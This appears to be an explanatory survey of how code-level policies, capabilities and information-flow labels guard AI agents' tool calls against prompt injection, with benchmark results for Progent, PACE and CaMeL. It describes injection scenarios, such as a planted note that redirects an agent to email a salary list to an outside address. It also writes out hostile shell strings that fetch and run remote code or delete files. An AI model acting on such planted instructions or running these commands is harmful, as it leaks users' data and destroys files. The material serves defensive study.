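# Typed action languages and capability restrictions for AI agents' tool calls

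## How agents call tools and why code checks the calls

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that can take actions, such as searching a mailbox or paying a bill. The model only produces text, so to take an action it writes a tool call, which is a structured request for the software to run a given function with given arguments. The software runs the function and returns the result, and the model continues from there.

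Much of the text an agent reads comes from people other than its user, and some of them may want the agent to do something the user never asked for. Security researchers address this in two broad ways. They make the model better at resisting, or they put ordinary code between the model and its tools, with rules about which calls may run. Typed action languages and capability restrictions take the second approach. They borrow from older work on operating systems and programming languages, and their appeal is that people can read the checking code and sometimes prove things about it, which nobody can yet do for a large language model. Safety still depends partly on the model, though, and how much varies a good deal from design to design.

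### The agent loop

Anthropic's *How tool use works*, written for developers who build on the company's Claude models, describes the loop in five steps. The application sends the model the user's message and a description of each tool. The model replies with one or more tool calls, each containing a tool name and a JSON object of arguments (JSON is a common text format for structured data). The application runs the functions. It then sends a new request containing the whole conversation so far, followed by the results. It repeats this process for as long as the model's replies contain tool calls. The model doesn't receive the tools' code or run anything itself.

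A group at Microsoft, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, write the same thing as two functions. With $F$ for the available tools and $D$ for the state of the mailbox, files and so on,

$$M : \text{Msg}^* \times F^* \to \text{ToolCall}\ f\ \textit{args} \;\mid\; \text{Assistant}\ r$$

$$f : D \times \text{str}^* \to D \times \text{str}$$

The model $M$ maps a list of messages and a list of tools to either a tool call or a final answer $r$. A tool $f$ takes the current state and some arguments, and returns a new state and some text. Only $f$ changes $D$, so an agent's actions can do damage only at the line of the loop that applies $f$. That line is therefore the natural place for a check.

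The check has to happen before the function runs, and developers can't always add one there. Anthropic runs the code for a few tools, such as web search, on its own servers, and the application usually sees the call only after it has finished. A developer can turn such a tool off but can't check each call before it runs.

Each message in a conversation has a role: system (the developer's standing instructions), user, assistant or tool. But before each query, the software flattens the conversation into one string, so the model receives a tool's output in the same stream as the user's request. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang et al., 2024) points out that language models have no formal way to tell instructions from data.

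### A request that a document can redirect

A user might tell an agent, "Send Bob the document he asked for; his address is in the meeting notes." The agent has tools to read the notes, fetch a document and send an email. If nothing goes wrong, it reads the notes, learns that Bob wanted the third-quarter report and that his address is bob@example.org, fetches the report and sends it. The user's request contains neither the address nor the document's name, so the agent has to get both from the notes.

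Now suppose someone else can edit the notes. She adds a sentence asking whoever handles the file to email the salary list to eve@example.net as well. This is indirect prompt injection, in which someone hides instructions in data that an agent reads, intending to redirect the agent. An ordinary agent may comply, and the software will send the salary list, because a call that the model made under someone else's influence looks like any other call. Security experts call this a confused-deputy problem, because an outsider chooses how the program uses the user's privileges.

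She could also make a less noticeable change and replace only Bob's address with her own. The agent would then make the calls the user wanted, in the right order, but with one wrong value. Limiting the agent to the tools that the task needs would stop neither attack, since both use the same tools as the user's task. Debenedetti and colleagues found this overlap in 17% of their test cases.

The quiet version is hard for any design to handle. *CapLite* (November 2026) lets an email go only to an address that appears word for word in the user's request. Here the request contains no address, so CapLite stops and asks the user to confirm. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) works through a very similar task, in which an agent looks up Alice's address and sends her parts of a report. The application names one directory as the authority on addresses, and the checking code accepts recipients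 only from there. If an attacker compromises the directory, the code will accept the wrong address. Both systems rely on a person or a designated source to determine which address to trust. Code can enforce that choice, but it cannot determine from the notes alone whether they can be trusted.

### Why training and filters give no guarantee

In most defences now in use, developers train or prompt the model to ignore instructions that appear in data, or they run a second model to screen incoming text for attacks. These measures lower the success rate of attacks, but each relies on a model's statistical judgement about whether a piece of text is an instruction, and an attacker can look for text that the model misjudges.

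*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, October 2025) showed how much that freedom matters. The team, drawn from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other organisations, tested 12 published defences, some against prompt injection and some against users who try to get forbidden output. They adapted their attacks to each defence and used plenty of computing power. The original papers reported attack success near zero for most of the 12 defences, but the adapted attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. Two defences that rely on careful prompting had let through as few as 1% of a standard set of fixed attacks, but they let through more than 95% of the adapted ones.

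The study does not rank the 12 defences, because each kept roughly the test setup of its original paper. It also cannot show that every future model will fail in the same way, and models have improved since. It does show that a low failure rate against a fixed list of attacks is very little evidence of safety against an attacker who keeps trying. Even an accurately measured failure rate of 1% is poor for an agent that can move money if the attacker can choose the attacks that succeed.

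### Assuming the model may output anything

The alternative starts from a pessimistic assumption. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (2026) states it plainly: the agent may propose any call and any arguments it can express, whether because of an attack, a malfunction or the ordinary pursuit of its task. Shivakumar and colleagues likewise set out to block forbidden calls even when the agent proposes them deliberately. The designer then tries to establish a statement of this form:

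$$\text{for every model } M \text{ and every state } d,\ \text{each call } c \text{ that runs satisfies } \textit{policy}(c)$$

The proof that an agent cannot make forbidden calls can be very short. If only one line of the program runs tools, and a policy check guards that line, then no model output can get a forbidden call through. This holds however clever the model is and whatever it has read. It holds even for a model that emits random characters, so it doesn't show that the agent can do useful work.

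The statement does not cover whether the policy is sensible or whether the model will choose well among the calls the policy permits. It also holds only if every route to a tool passes through the check, which is easy to specify but harder to ensure when one of the tools is a command line.

Some designs in this family are less pessimistic. Costa and colleagues trust the model, the user's messages and the tool descriptions, and treat the data that tools return as the danger. Their checks can establish that no untrusted text influenced a call, but a call may still pass if the model misreads a legitimate request. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) similarly requires that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input cannot trigger an action with harmful side effects. Both assumptions are reasonable, but they rely on the model for safety to different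 degrees.

### A well-formed call can still be the wrong call

Most systems already run a limited check on tool calls using each tool's schema, which describes the arguments the tool takes and the form of each. Software can validate a finished call against the schema and reject it if it doesn't fit, or it can prevent invalid calls through constrained decoding. A language model writes one token (a word or piece of a word) at a time, choosing from a probability distribution over its vocabulary. In constrained decoding, as *Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations* (2026) describes it, a checker determines at each step which tokens could validly continue the text, sets the probability of all others to zero, and lets the model choose from the rest.

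Anthropic's *Strict tool use* describes a setting that guarantees that the tool's name exists and that the arguments match the schema. For example, a booking function that expects a whole number of passengers will get `2`, not `"two"`. The guarantee has small exceptions. Anthropic's *Structured outputs*, which documents the November 2025 test version, says the output may not match the schema if the model refuses or the reply hits the length limit. That version also could not enforce numerical ranges while the model was writing.

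The larger safety problem is that a schema describes only the form of a call's arguments. It can require that `recipient` be an email address, but eve@example.net meets that requirement. Every call in the redirected version of Bob's request is well formed and would pass the schema check.

Even without an attacker, a well-formed call can be wrong. Verma (2026), in *Inference for Reasoning Models*, measured small open models on a standard test of function calling, with and without a schema constraint. For Qwen3-8B, the constraint raised the share of well-formed calls by 15.5 percentage points and the share of correct calls by 5.5. Llama-3.1-8B and Mistral-7B already produced well-formed calls every time, and the constraint did not improve their accuracy, which stayed near 55%. When no available tool applied to a request, Mistral-7B still called one more than half the time. Stronger models make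 fewer such mistakes, but not because of the schema. *Constrained Decoding for Diffusion Language Models via Efficient Inference over Finite Automata* (2026) also reports calls that fit the schema completely but contain the wrong value.

Some errors can't be detected from a single call. *Agents as Software* (Barke and Murali, 2026) gives the example of a refund with a valid order number and amount, for goods that the customer hasn't yet returned. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes an email that passes every type check even though its body contains customer data from a different task.

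Constrained decoding can serve safety when it enforces a security policy. *Only What You've Signed up For* (2026) uses a policy specific to the task. If the user asks to share a report with Alice, view-only, the decoder cannot produce a call that grants edit access or names another recipient. *AGDecode* (2026) also goes beyond grammar to constraints on meaning, and reports that existing methods of that sort are much slower. When the constraint comes from a security policy, the policy provides the safety, and a check right before the tool runs could also enforce it.

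### The basic vocabulary

A *policy* is a rule, enforced by code, about which tool calls may run and with which arguments. For Bob's request, a strict one might read:

```
allow send_email if recipient = bob@example.org and attachment = q3-report.pdf
refuse every other send_email
```

The difficulty with this one is obvious. Somebody has to know Bob's address before writing it.

A *capability* is an unforgeable value that gives its holder the right to perform a particular action. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) defines it as a pair $\text{Cap}[e, \varphi]$, where $e$ is a kind of effect, such as reading or writing, and $\varphi$ is a test on the call's arguments. A capability covers a call if the tool has effect $e$ and the arguments pass $\varphi$, and a call runs only if a capability covers it.

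```
agent holds:   Cap[send, recipient = bob@example.org]
agent tries:   send_email(recipient = eve@example.net, ...)   -> refused
```

CapScope, a system for coding agents, keeps capabilities in a table outside the conversation, where the model can neither read nor change them. Each sub-agent has its own table, so one that runs tests has no right to edit the source code, even if it reads a planted instruction in the test output. In 300 trials on five repair tasks, the injected action went through in 3 of 75 runs with CapScope, compared with 33 to 47 of 75 in each of the three other setups. The agent completed 68 repairs with CapScope and 68 to 72 in the other setups. An injection can still misuse any right legitimately held by the agent that reads it. A language model proposes the initial set of rights from the user's request and the names of the project's files, and ordinary code validates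 and freezes it before the agent opens a file. Part of the policy is therefore still a model's guess, but the model makes it before seeing any file contents from an attacker.

A *type* is a class of values, and a type checker rejects a program that puts a value of the wrong class somewhere. How much a type protects depends on how narrow it is:

```
recipient : String            accepts bob@example.org and eve@example.net
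recipient : DirectoryEntry    accepts only what the company directory returned
```

Types can also include conditions. Barke and Murali suggest a refund type that allows only amounts above zero and no greater than the order's total. Some type checks can run on a plan or program before the agent starts, which catches a bad step before any earlier step has taken effect. Other checks have to wait for values that only appear during the run.

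A *label* is a mark on a piece of data. It records who may read the data (confidentiality) and who may have influenced it (integrity). In the simplest scheme each half has two values, public or secret and trusted or untrusted:

```
the user's request    trusted, public
the meeting notes     untrusted, secret
```

Finally, the *trusted components* are the parts that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold. Computer security calls them the trusted computing base.

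```
must be right:   the checker, the policy, the labels on inputs, the email tool
may be wrong:    the model's output, the text of the notes
```

Shivakumar and colleagues wrote the core of their checker in Lean, a language in which a computer verifies proofs about programs. Their guarantee still holds only if the Python code passes calls to that core correctly, the application describes its own tools accurately, and the functions meant to remove private fields do remove them.

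### How labels spread

Labels would be of little use if they stayed on the original files. The address that the model copies out of the notes is a new piece of text, and it needs a label too. The standard rule is that derived data takes the combined label of everything that went into it. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, write this as

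$$\ell_z = \ell_x \sqcup \ell_y$$

for data $z$ derived from $x$ and $y$. With two values on each side the operation $\sqcup$ is simple: one untrusted input makes the result untrusted, and one secret input makes it secret. (FIDES, the system of Costa and colleagues, also has richer labels that list individual readers and writers.) Carrying labels along in this way, and blocking the flows that a policy forbids, is information-flow control.

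In Bob's case, the request is trusted and public, while the notes are untrusted and secret. Once the notes are in the conversation, the rule labels everything the model writes afterwards as untrusted and secret, including the call that sends the report to the correct address. A policy that permits emails only on the basis of trusted data will therefore block the legitimate email as well as the malicious one. Nobody can reliably trace which parts of its input a language model used, so the rule treats the model as having used all of them.

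Much work in the field tries to relax this restriction without giving up the guarantee. CaMeL keeps the notes away from the planner model, which decides on the tool calls, and has a separate quarantined model without tools read them. Another approach is to change the data's labels deliberately. Endorsement marks untrusted data as trusted, for instance after the user has looked at it, and declassification marks secret data as less secret. In the report task of Shivakumar and colleagues, a function copies only the approved fields of a confidential report, and the application declares its output public. As they note, changing a label removes nothing secret from the text. If the function also copies a field that wasn't approved, the checker will still allow the output.

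### AgentDojo, the common yardstick

Debenedetti and colleagues built AgentDojo to measure both whether an agent resists injections and whether it still completes the user's tasks. It simulates four settings, called suites, each with its own tools, data, user tasks, and injection tasks, which are the attacker's goals. The benchmark pairs each user task with each injection task in the same suite and places the attacker's text where the agent is likely to read it, such as in the body of an email.

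| Suite | Tools | User tasks | Injection tasks | Pairs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack (team messages, web pages) | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel (hotels, flights, restaurants) | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 74 | 97 | 27 | 629 |

One of the Slack tasks has the same form as Bob's request. The user asks the agent to invite Dora and says that her email address is on her website.

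After each task, ordinary code inspects the state of the simulated world to check whether, for example, the email was sent. The designers avoided using a language model as judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge. The benchmark reports three scores. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes with no attack present. Utility under attack is the share of pairs in which the agent completes the user's task and the attack causes no side effects. Targeted attack success is the share of pairs in which the attacker's goal is achieved. An agent that refuses every call scores zero on targeted attack success but does no useful work, so security scores should be reported with utility scores.

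The benchmark has grown since 2024. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts more than 900 pairs, so results from different years may be based on different sets. The benchmark is still widely used. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026), for example, ran 13 models from six providers on all four suites. A newer benchmark, AgentDyn, has longer tasks that force the agent to change its plan partway through. As *StepGuard* (2026) describes it, AgentDyn also includes third-party instructions that the agent should follow, and designs that treat everything a tool returns as untrusted have difficulty with these.

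A low attack score on AgentDojo means different things for different defences. Attack success against the two prompting defences rose from 1% to above 95% on this same benchmark. The security argument for a defence that enforces a policy in code depends on the proof and the trusted components, so an attack score of zero mostly confirms that someone wrote policies covering AgentDojo's 27 attacker goals. The utility scores are more informative for such a defence, because they show how much legitimate work those policies also block.

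## Tool allowlists, argument rules and capability tokens: Progent and PACE

The simplest policy for an agent is an allowlist, a list of the tools it may call. Software checks each tool call and refuses it if the tool isn't on the list. That can be enough for an agent that only looks things up, because an injected instruction to move money fails if the list contains no payment tool.

The list protects much less once the task itself is a payment. Suppose a user asks a banking agent to pay the July electricity bill. The allowlist must then include `send_money`, and that one name covers all of these calls:

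```
send_money(recipient = "CITY-POWER", amount = 84)      the bill
send_money(recipient = "CITY-POWER", amount = 8400)    a misread decimal point
send_money(recipient = "EVE-99",     amount = 84)      a theft
```

A useful policy therefore has to constrain the arguments as well. AgentDojo includes a coarser defence, the tool filter, in which a model picks the tools for a task before the agent starts and the software removes the rest. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) found that this filter blocked more legitimate work and let through more attacks than its own rules on arguments, because the filter could only keep or remove whole tools.

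### Progent's rules

Progent is a small language for writing such rules, together with software that applies them to each call. A rule has five parts:

```
effect   tool   when { conditions }   fallback action   priority number
```

The effect is either allow or forbid. The conditions test the call's arguments. They can compare numbers, look up a value in a list, check the length of a list or match text against a pattern, and they can be combined with "and", "or" and "not". The fallback is what Progent does when it blocks a call. Progent can stop the agent, ask the user or return a message to the model. By default, it returns a message that explains the refusal and suggests trying other tools or arguments.

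A policy for the electricity bill might contain two rules:

```
forbid send_money when { not (amount ≤ 500) }
       fallback request user inspection           priority 1

allow  send_money when { recipient == "CITY-POWER" }
       fallback return "Payment not allowed"      priority 1
```

For each call, Progent collects the rules for that tool and sorts them by priority, putting forbid rules before allow rules when priorities are equal. The first rule whose conditions hold decides the matter. If none holds, Progent blocks the call. The three payments then go as follows:

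```
                                     forbid rule   allow rule   outcome
send_money("CITY-POWER", 84)         no match      match        runs
send_money("CITY-POWER", 8400)       match         not reached  user decides
send_money("EVE-99", 84)             no match      no match     blocked
```

The payment to Eve fails because no rule allows it, so nobody had to know about her in advance. It would fail whatever the model had read. But each rule tests only the arguments of a single call, so ten payments of 500 to the power company would all go through unless the policy changed in between.

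Even short rules like these can combine in ways their author didn't intend. An earlier version of the Progent paper describes two checks for this. A type checker rejects a condition that doesn't fit its argument, such as one that asks for the third element of something that isn't a list. An overlap analyser checks whether any call could satisfy both rules in each pair for the same tool. It uses Z3, a program that decides whether a set of logical conditions can all hold at once. The two rules above overlap because a payment of 8,400 to the power company matches both, so the rules' author gets a warning and can confirm that the forbid rule should win. The current version of the paper leaves out both checks and uses Z3 for a different task involving policies that a model writes.

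Installing Progent requires little change to an agent. Developers can wrap the tools with a few lines of code, or users can route an existing agent's traffic through a proxy. The proxy can't guard tools built into the agent, because calls to those tools never pass through it.

### Letting a model write the policy

A developer can write general rules once, for instance that an agent may never delete a database. Other rules depend on the request, such as one that names this month's payee, and few users would write new ones every time. Before the agent starts, Progent can have a language model write a policy for the task from the tool definitions and the user's request.

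Sometimes the user's request doesn't contain enough information to write a narrow policy. Shi and colleagues give the example of a user who asks a banking agent to send money to Apple on the basis of past transactions. The request doesn't include Apple's account number, so the first policy has to let `send_money` pay any account. Once another tool returns the number, the policy can restrict payments to that account. Other tasks need wider permissions as they go on. An agent collecting employees' hobbies from Slack might find a link to someone's blog and need permission to open it.

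Progent therefore lets the model revise the policy after a tool call, which leaves part of the decision to a model that is reading untrusted output. An attacker who can write into that output can ask the model to permit the theft. Two measures give some protection, though both depend on the model's judgement. The model first decides whether an update might be needed, and at this step it sees the tool call but not its result. The prompt for the update then instructs the model to grant only what the user's task requires.

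The stronger protection is the solver's new job. Let $P$ be the set of calls that the current policy allows and $P'$ the set that the proposed policy would allow. The solver looks for a call in $P'$ that is not in $P$:

$$\exists\, c :\ c \in P' \ \text{and}\ c \notin P$$

If there is no such call, the update is a narrowing and takes effect at once. Otherwise it is an expansion, and by default somebody has to approve it. Without approval, injected text therefore cannot expand the set of permitted calls beyond the initial policy, which the model wrote before seeing any tool results.

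This answers the criticism for updates that widen the policy, but it helps less when the first policy was already loose. In the Apple example, the first policy permits a payment to anyone. A forged transaction record could therefore lead the model to narrow the policy to the attacker's account, and the solver would correctly accept the change as a narrowing. Shi and colleagues address this by treating the tool that returns account numbers as a trusted source, which leaves the developer to judge whether it deserves that trust.

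### How well Progent does in tests

Progent cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%, with little change in utility, when OpenAI's GPT-4o both ran the agent and wrote the policies. On Agent Security Bench, a collection of ten agent scenarios, it cut the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded there used malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones. Handwritten rules reduced the rate there to zero.

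In both experiments, Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically to imitate a user who agrees to everything. This effectively switched off the solver's check, so the results test the policy-writing model. Attack success was lower still when the team refused every expansion. It fell to zero when a person reviewed the first policy and each expansion, though the experiment assumed that this reviewer never granted unrestricted payments and always rejected a malicious address. Only 6% of updates were expansions, which limits the number of approval requests. People who face many such requests tend to stop reading them.

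The team also tested attacks aimed at the update step, two with fixed wording and one with an automated search. In the earlier version of the paper, these raised the attack success rate from 2.2% to 4.0%; the current version again reports a small increase. This is encouraging, but the test was probably lighter than the one in which Nasr and colleagues broke most of the 12 defences they examined. The AgentDojo figures also leave out two attacks that steer the agent towards a different, equally legitimate hotel, a booking that no permission rule could distinguish from the right one.

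*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) compared its own system with Progent on other benchmarks and reported much weaker results for Progent. On MCPTox, where the attacker writes the tool descriptions, the most effective group of attacks still succeeded in 9% to 46% of cases with Progent, depending on the model. A plain tool allowlist let fewer of these attacks through with all three models. On PASB, which tests a personal assistant running on the user's own computer, the range with Progent was 63% to 80%. The exact numbers deserve some caution, because teams don't always get the best out of a rival's system. A plausible reason for the MCPTox result is that Progent's policy-writing model reads the tool definitions, so the attacker's text reaches it before the first policy exists.

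### Which requirements simple checks can enforce

Attack benchmarks give little information about the rules a business would want to enforce. *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (Hong, She and colleagues, 2026) looked for such rules in 80 benchmarks for agent security and safety and found that 85% contained no requirement stated precisely enough to check. The researchers then studied three cases closely: an airline's customer service agent, a voice assistant in a car, and an assistant for medical records. The first two came with written policies, and they had language models draft one for the third.

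After removing statements that weren't really requirements, they had 126 left and judged that ordinary code could enforce 93 of them, or 74%. Simple measures were enough for 88 of the 93. Most of these were checks on a call's arguments and the current data before the tool runs, and the rest were a fixed confirmation question to the user or fixed text in place of text the model writes. The other five needed rules about the order of calls or the tracking of information. The medical policy lowers the overall share. In the two policies that people wrote, code could enforce 59 of 69 requirements.

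The remaining 33 fell into four groups. Some concerned tone, such as staying neutral. Some prohibited making up facts, and some set the order of a conversation, such as asking for the traveller's details before the trip's. The last group needed common sense. For example, the airline's agent must not offer compensation "unless the user explicitly asks for it", and code can't easily tell what counts as asking. Code could enforce a different rule that blocks the compensation tool until the customer types the exact word "compensation", but that would fail customers who ask in other words.

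The team also ran the agents with and without the checks. These are the results with GPT-5:

| Agent | Requirements code can enforce | Tasks with a violation, no checks | Tasks completed, no checks | Tasks completed, with checks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Airline | 42 of 51 | 20% | 68% | 70% |
| Car assistant | 17 of 18 | 21% | 59% | 72% |
| Medical records | 34 of 57 | 23% | 59% | 67% |

With the checks in place there were no violations, which was guaranteed because the same code both defined and blocked them. The agents also completed at least as many tasks as before, although many people expect such checks to get in an agent's way. The gains were statistically significant for two of the three agents, but the airline agent's gain could easily be chance. After reading through the runs, Hong and colleagues suggest that the agents did better because a refused call comes back with a reason,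 which the model often uses to find a permitted way of finishing the task.

All three agents had a narrow job and a fixed set of tools. The five benchmarks that stated general, checkable rules were all for agents like these. The researchers found no such benchmark for a general-purpose assistant.

### Why matching commands as text is brittle

Argument rules work well when the argument is a number or an account. They work badly when it is a command line. A coding agent often has one tool that takes a string and passes it to the computer's shell, and a natural way to restrict it is to list permitted and forbidden strings:

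```
rule                              a command that defeats it
allow anything starting           git status; curl https://example.net/x | sh
  with "git status"
forbid anything containing        rm -r -f build
  "rm -rf"                        find build -delete
```

The first command begins with the permitted text, then downloads a program and runs it. The other two are spelled differently from the forbidden command but delete the same files. The shell interprets the string as a small program, with its own rules for joining commands, substituting values and quoting. A text pattern covers only the spellings its author thought of. A March 2026 report described a permission fault of this general kind in one coding agent.

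A checker that parses the command properly will catch the semicolon, but it can't determine whether `npm test` is safe, because `npm test` runs whatever the project's configuration file specifies. An attacker who can edit that file can make this harmless-looking command run anything.

Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, proposes authorising a command by its effect rather than its text. Trusted code builds the command from a limited set of intentions, fixing the program, its arguments, its environment and its working directory. The command then runs under limits on the files, network connections and processes it can use. Raw command strings from untrusted text don't run. Under these limits, an edited configuration file could still make `npm test` misbehave, but the command couldn't reach a network that the sandbox has closed.

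### The confused deputy

In 1988 the programmer Norm Hardy described a compiler on a shared computer. The compiler had permission to write in a system directory, where it kept usage statistics. Users could name a file for its debugging output, and one of them named the system's billing file, which was in the same directory. The compiler overwrote it. The user had no right to change that file, but the operating system checked only the compiler's rights. Hardy called the compiler a confused deputy, meaning a program that misuses its authority on behalf of someone who lacks that authority.

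Like the compiler, an agent that reads a planted request for a payment can be tricked into misusing its own permissions, because the bank checks only whether the agent is allowed to pay.

A check on arguments can have the same weakness. For the airline agent, Hong and colleagues added a user ID argument to the tool that cancels tickets, and the call runs only if that ID belongs to the ticket's owner. But the model supplies the ID, so an attacker who can get the model to enter the owner's ID will pass the check. The check is reliable only if other code ties the ID to the logged-in user.

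Capabilities prevent this by combining a reference to a resource with the right to act on it. If Hardy's user had needed to supply a capability to write to the output file, the trick would have failed, because the user had none for the billing file. Similarly, a payment request in a web page's text can't give an agent the right to make the payment. In some systems, the agent writes programs in which a compiler tracks capabilities as types. Others check capabilities just before each tool call.

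### How PACE issues and checks capabilities

PACE, short for Provenance-Aware Capability Enforcement, is a system of the second sort, from October 2026. Each capability records a purpose, a resource, limits on the arguments, a budget, an expiry time, and how far the holder may pass the right on. For the electricity bill it might look like this:

```
purpose      pay the July electricity bill
resource     the user's current account
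arguments    recipient = CITY-POWER, amount ≤ 84
budget       one payment
expiry       end of this session
delegation   none
```

The budget closes the gap that let ten separate payments through under the Progent rules above.

Ordinary code issues the capability, using only the user's authenticated request and rules fixed in advance. It doesn't read web pages, tool results or anything a model has written, so none of these can create or widen a capability. This is firmer than relying on Progent's model-written policies, but it needs more preparation. Li and colleagues wrote policies and tool descriptions for each benchmark before the final runs, using its published interfaces and task formats. Their results don't show how well fixed code would turn an ordinary user's loosely worded request into the right capability.

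When the model proposes a call, PACE first stores a copy of the arguments so that they can't change during the check. It then works out the call's effects from the tool's description: what operation it performs, on which resource, and whether the result lasts. Each effect has to pass nine tests:

- A capability covers it.
- The arguments have the right types and stay within their limits.
- The operation and the party performing it are the permitted ones.
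- It respects confidentiality.
- Any lasting change is permitted.
- A right that one agent passed to another hasn't grown on the way.
- Enough of the budget remains.
- The request and the recorded state are still current.
- The software is able to intervene at this point.

PACE makes a second, separate check on where the data came from. It keeps a graph of the values in a session and the calls they went into, and looks for paths that lead from untrusted or secret data to an unsafe effect. It then finds the cheapest set of links to cut so that no such path remains. Only links belonging to the current call can still be cut. Every path enters the call through one of its arguments and leaves through the single link $e_T$ from the call to its effect. If $A^*$ is the set of links for arguments that such data can reach, a set of cuts works only if it contains $e_T$ or all of $A^*$, and the cheapest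 cut $C$ therefore costs

$$\text{cost}(C) = \min\{\text{cost}(e_T),\ \text{cost}(A^*)\}$$

PACE can block the call or remove every affected argument. Removing an argument is safe only if the model would have made the call without it, and usually no one can guarantee that about a language model. In practice, the second check, the data check, nearly always blocks the call. If the agent read the amount of the electricity bill in an email, this check stops the payment even though the user asked for it. In a trial on part of AgentDojo, the data check alone reduced the share of tasks completed from 76.8% to 13.6%. On AgentDyn, which has longer and more changeable tasks, it reduced the share from 66.7% to zero.

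This is why the paper describes two versions. In PACE-C a call must pass both checks, and the paper's proofs about paths from untrusted data apply to this version. In PACE-P the capability check can restore a call that the data check has blocked. PACE-P also releases some calls with minor, reversible effects even when no capability covers them, and it can repair a call in ways the developers declared in advance without checking the repaired call again. Li and colleagues ran all their experiments on PACE-P, so the proofs about paths don't cover the system they measured. They argue that PACE-P has a weaker property. An unauthorised effect that is irreversible or reaches the outside world can happen only through one of the declared repairs, provided that the tool descriptions and the issuing code are right and every call passes through PACE.

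### What PACE stops and what it allows

The team tested PACE-P on eight benchmarks with three models. In 79 comparisons with other defences, each for one model and one group of attacks, it had the lowest attack success in 62 and tied for the lowest in 14. The AgentDojo results, for the most effective group of attacks on each model, were:

| Model | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, PACE-P | Utility, no defence | Utility, PACE-P |
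|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-3.8-27B | 48.0% | 0.0% | 62.6% | 59.7% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 99.8% | 5.1% | 75.7% | 75.3% |
| GPT-5.6-luna | 100.0% | 8.1% | 73.8% | 72.1% |

Results elsewhere were less even. On one version of the InjecAgent benchmark, attacks on GPT-5.6-luna still succeeded 31% of the time.

Most of the protection came from the capabilities. In the trial on part of AgentDojo with the Qwen model, the capability check alone reduced attack success from 37.4% to zero. Utility was 64.6%, compared with 67.2% for the complete system. Li and colleagues acknowledge that the complete system showed no security benefit over a simpler version. The loss of utility can also be larger than the table shows. On the AgentDyn part of that trial, the complete system reduced the share of completed tasks from 66.7% to 33.3%, although the loss on the whole benchmark was under three percentage points.

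The team also let a model search for better attacks, with up to 50 attempts per case. It succeeded in 21 of 30 cases against an undefended agent and in none against PACE-P, though with so few cases, the true rate against PACE-P could be as high as 11%. More importantly, the researchers chose only cases in which the capability didn't cover what the attacker wanted. They found that this was true of only 375 of the 629 pairs of tasks and attacks in AgentDojo. In the other 254 (40%), the user's own request had produced a capability broad enough to allow the attack.

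That is well above the 17% overlap in tools that Debenedetti and colleagues counted, which suggests that the capabilities were often broader than necessary. The share was high in the banking suite, where the capability covered the attacker's call in 84 of 144 pairs. The search for better attacks left that suite out, so the zero is weak evidence about payments. Protection for payments depends largely on whether the issuing code can specify the payee and the amount or only grant the right to pay.

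### One capability for one action

A PACE capability can cover many different calls until its budget runs out or it expires. In Context-to-Execution Integrity, published in July 2026, a capability authorizes one exact action. The host software writes a description of the proposed action, including the account it will run under and the current state of the files it will change. It then looks for three separate permissions that match this description: one for each sensitive argument, one for the effect, and one for the call itself. A ledger marks the call permission as used before the tool runs. If the agent repeats the call, or if anything in the description changes after the check, the old permission is no longer valid.

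The system also allows limited use of facts from untrusted text. An agent repairing software may need a file name from an error log that an attacker could have written. Trusted code can check that the name is a valid path in the project and allow its use only as the file argument. The log can't determine which tool is called or count as approval for the change. In 192 test cases, Santos-Grueiro found that checking calls against a schema still let an unauthorised action run in every case, while the full system let none run.

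In 400 software tasks with live models, no unauthorised action passed the check, and the agents completed 231 tasks safely. Of the rest, 73 failed because the software couldn't parse the model's output, 61 because the proposed effect wasn't authorised, and 35 because the authorised change didn't solve the problem.

All of this depends on somebody classifying every argument of every tool correctly. Santos-Grueiro audited the policies for 24 kinds of action, with 149 arguments in total, and found 18 faults on the first pass, nine of them serious. The faults included treating arguments that could change a program's behaviour as plain text, and accepting approvals written in ordinary prose. The final audit found no faults that would block use, but it covered only the policies in the experiments.

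## Planning before reading untrusted data: CaMeL

Progent and PACE check calls from a model that may already have read an attacker's text. CaMeL, which a team at Google DeepMind published in 2025, instead has the model choose its calls before it reads anything an attacker could have written. It builds on a simpler proposal from two years earlier.

### Two models and a set of variables

Simon Willison, the programmer who named prompt injection, set out that proposal on his blog in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023). The proposal splits an assistant into two language models and an ordinary program called the controller. The planner model takes the user's request and can call tools, but never sees text from emails, web pages or other untrusted sources. The quarantined model reads that text and has no tools. The design assumes that this model could "go rogue at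 any moment".

The controller runs the tools and stores each result in a variable. It tells the planner model only the variable's name. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the planner model gives three instructions, one after another:

```
$VAR1 = fetch_latest_emails(1)
$VAR2 = quarantined_llm("Summarize this: $VAR1")
display("Your latest email, summarized: $VAR2")
```

The controller inserts the email's text when it calls the quarantined model, and inserts the summary when it displays the answer. If the email contains an instruction to delete the inbox, only the quarantined model reads it, and that model can't delete anything.

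Willison allowed one exception. The planner model may see an answer from the quarantined model if software can verify that the answer is harmless, for instance by checking that it is one of a fixed set of categories. Looser limits are risky. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* suggests that a coding agent could safely read outside documentation if a quarantined model first reduced it to a strict format, with method names of at most 30 characters. In a post about the paper, Willison pointed out that an attacker might still do harm with a name that fits the limit, such as `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`.

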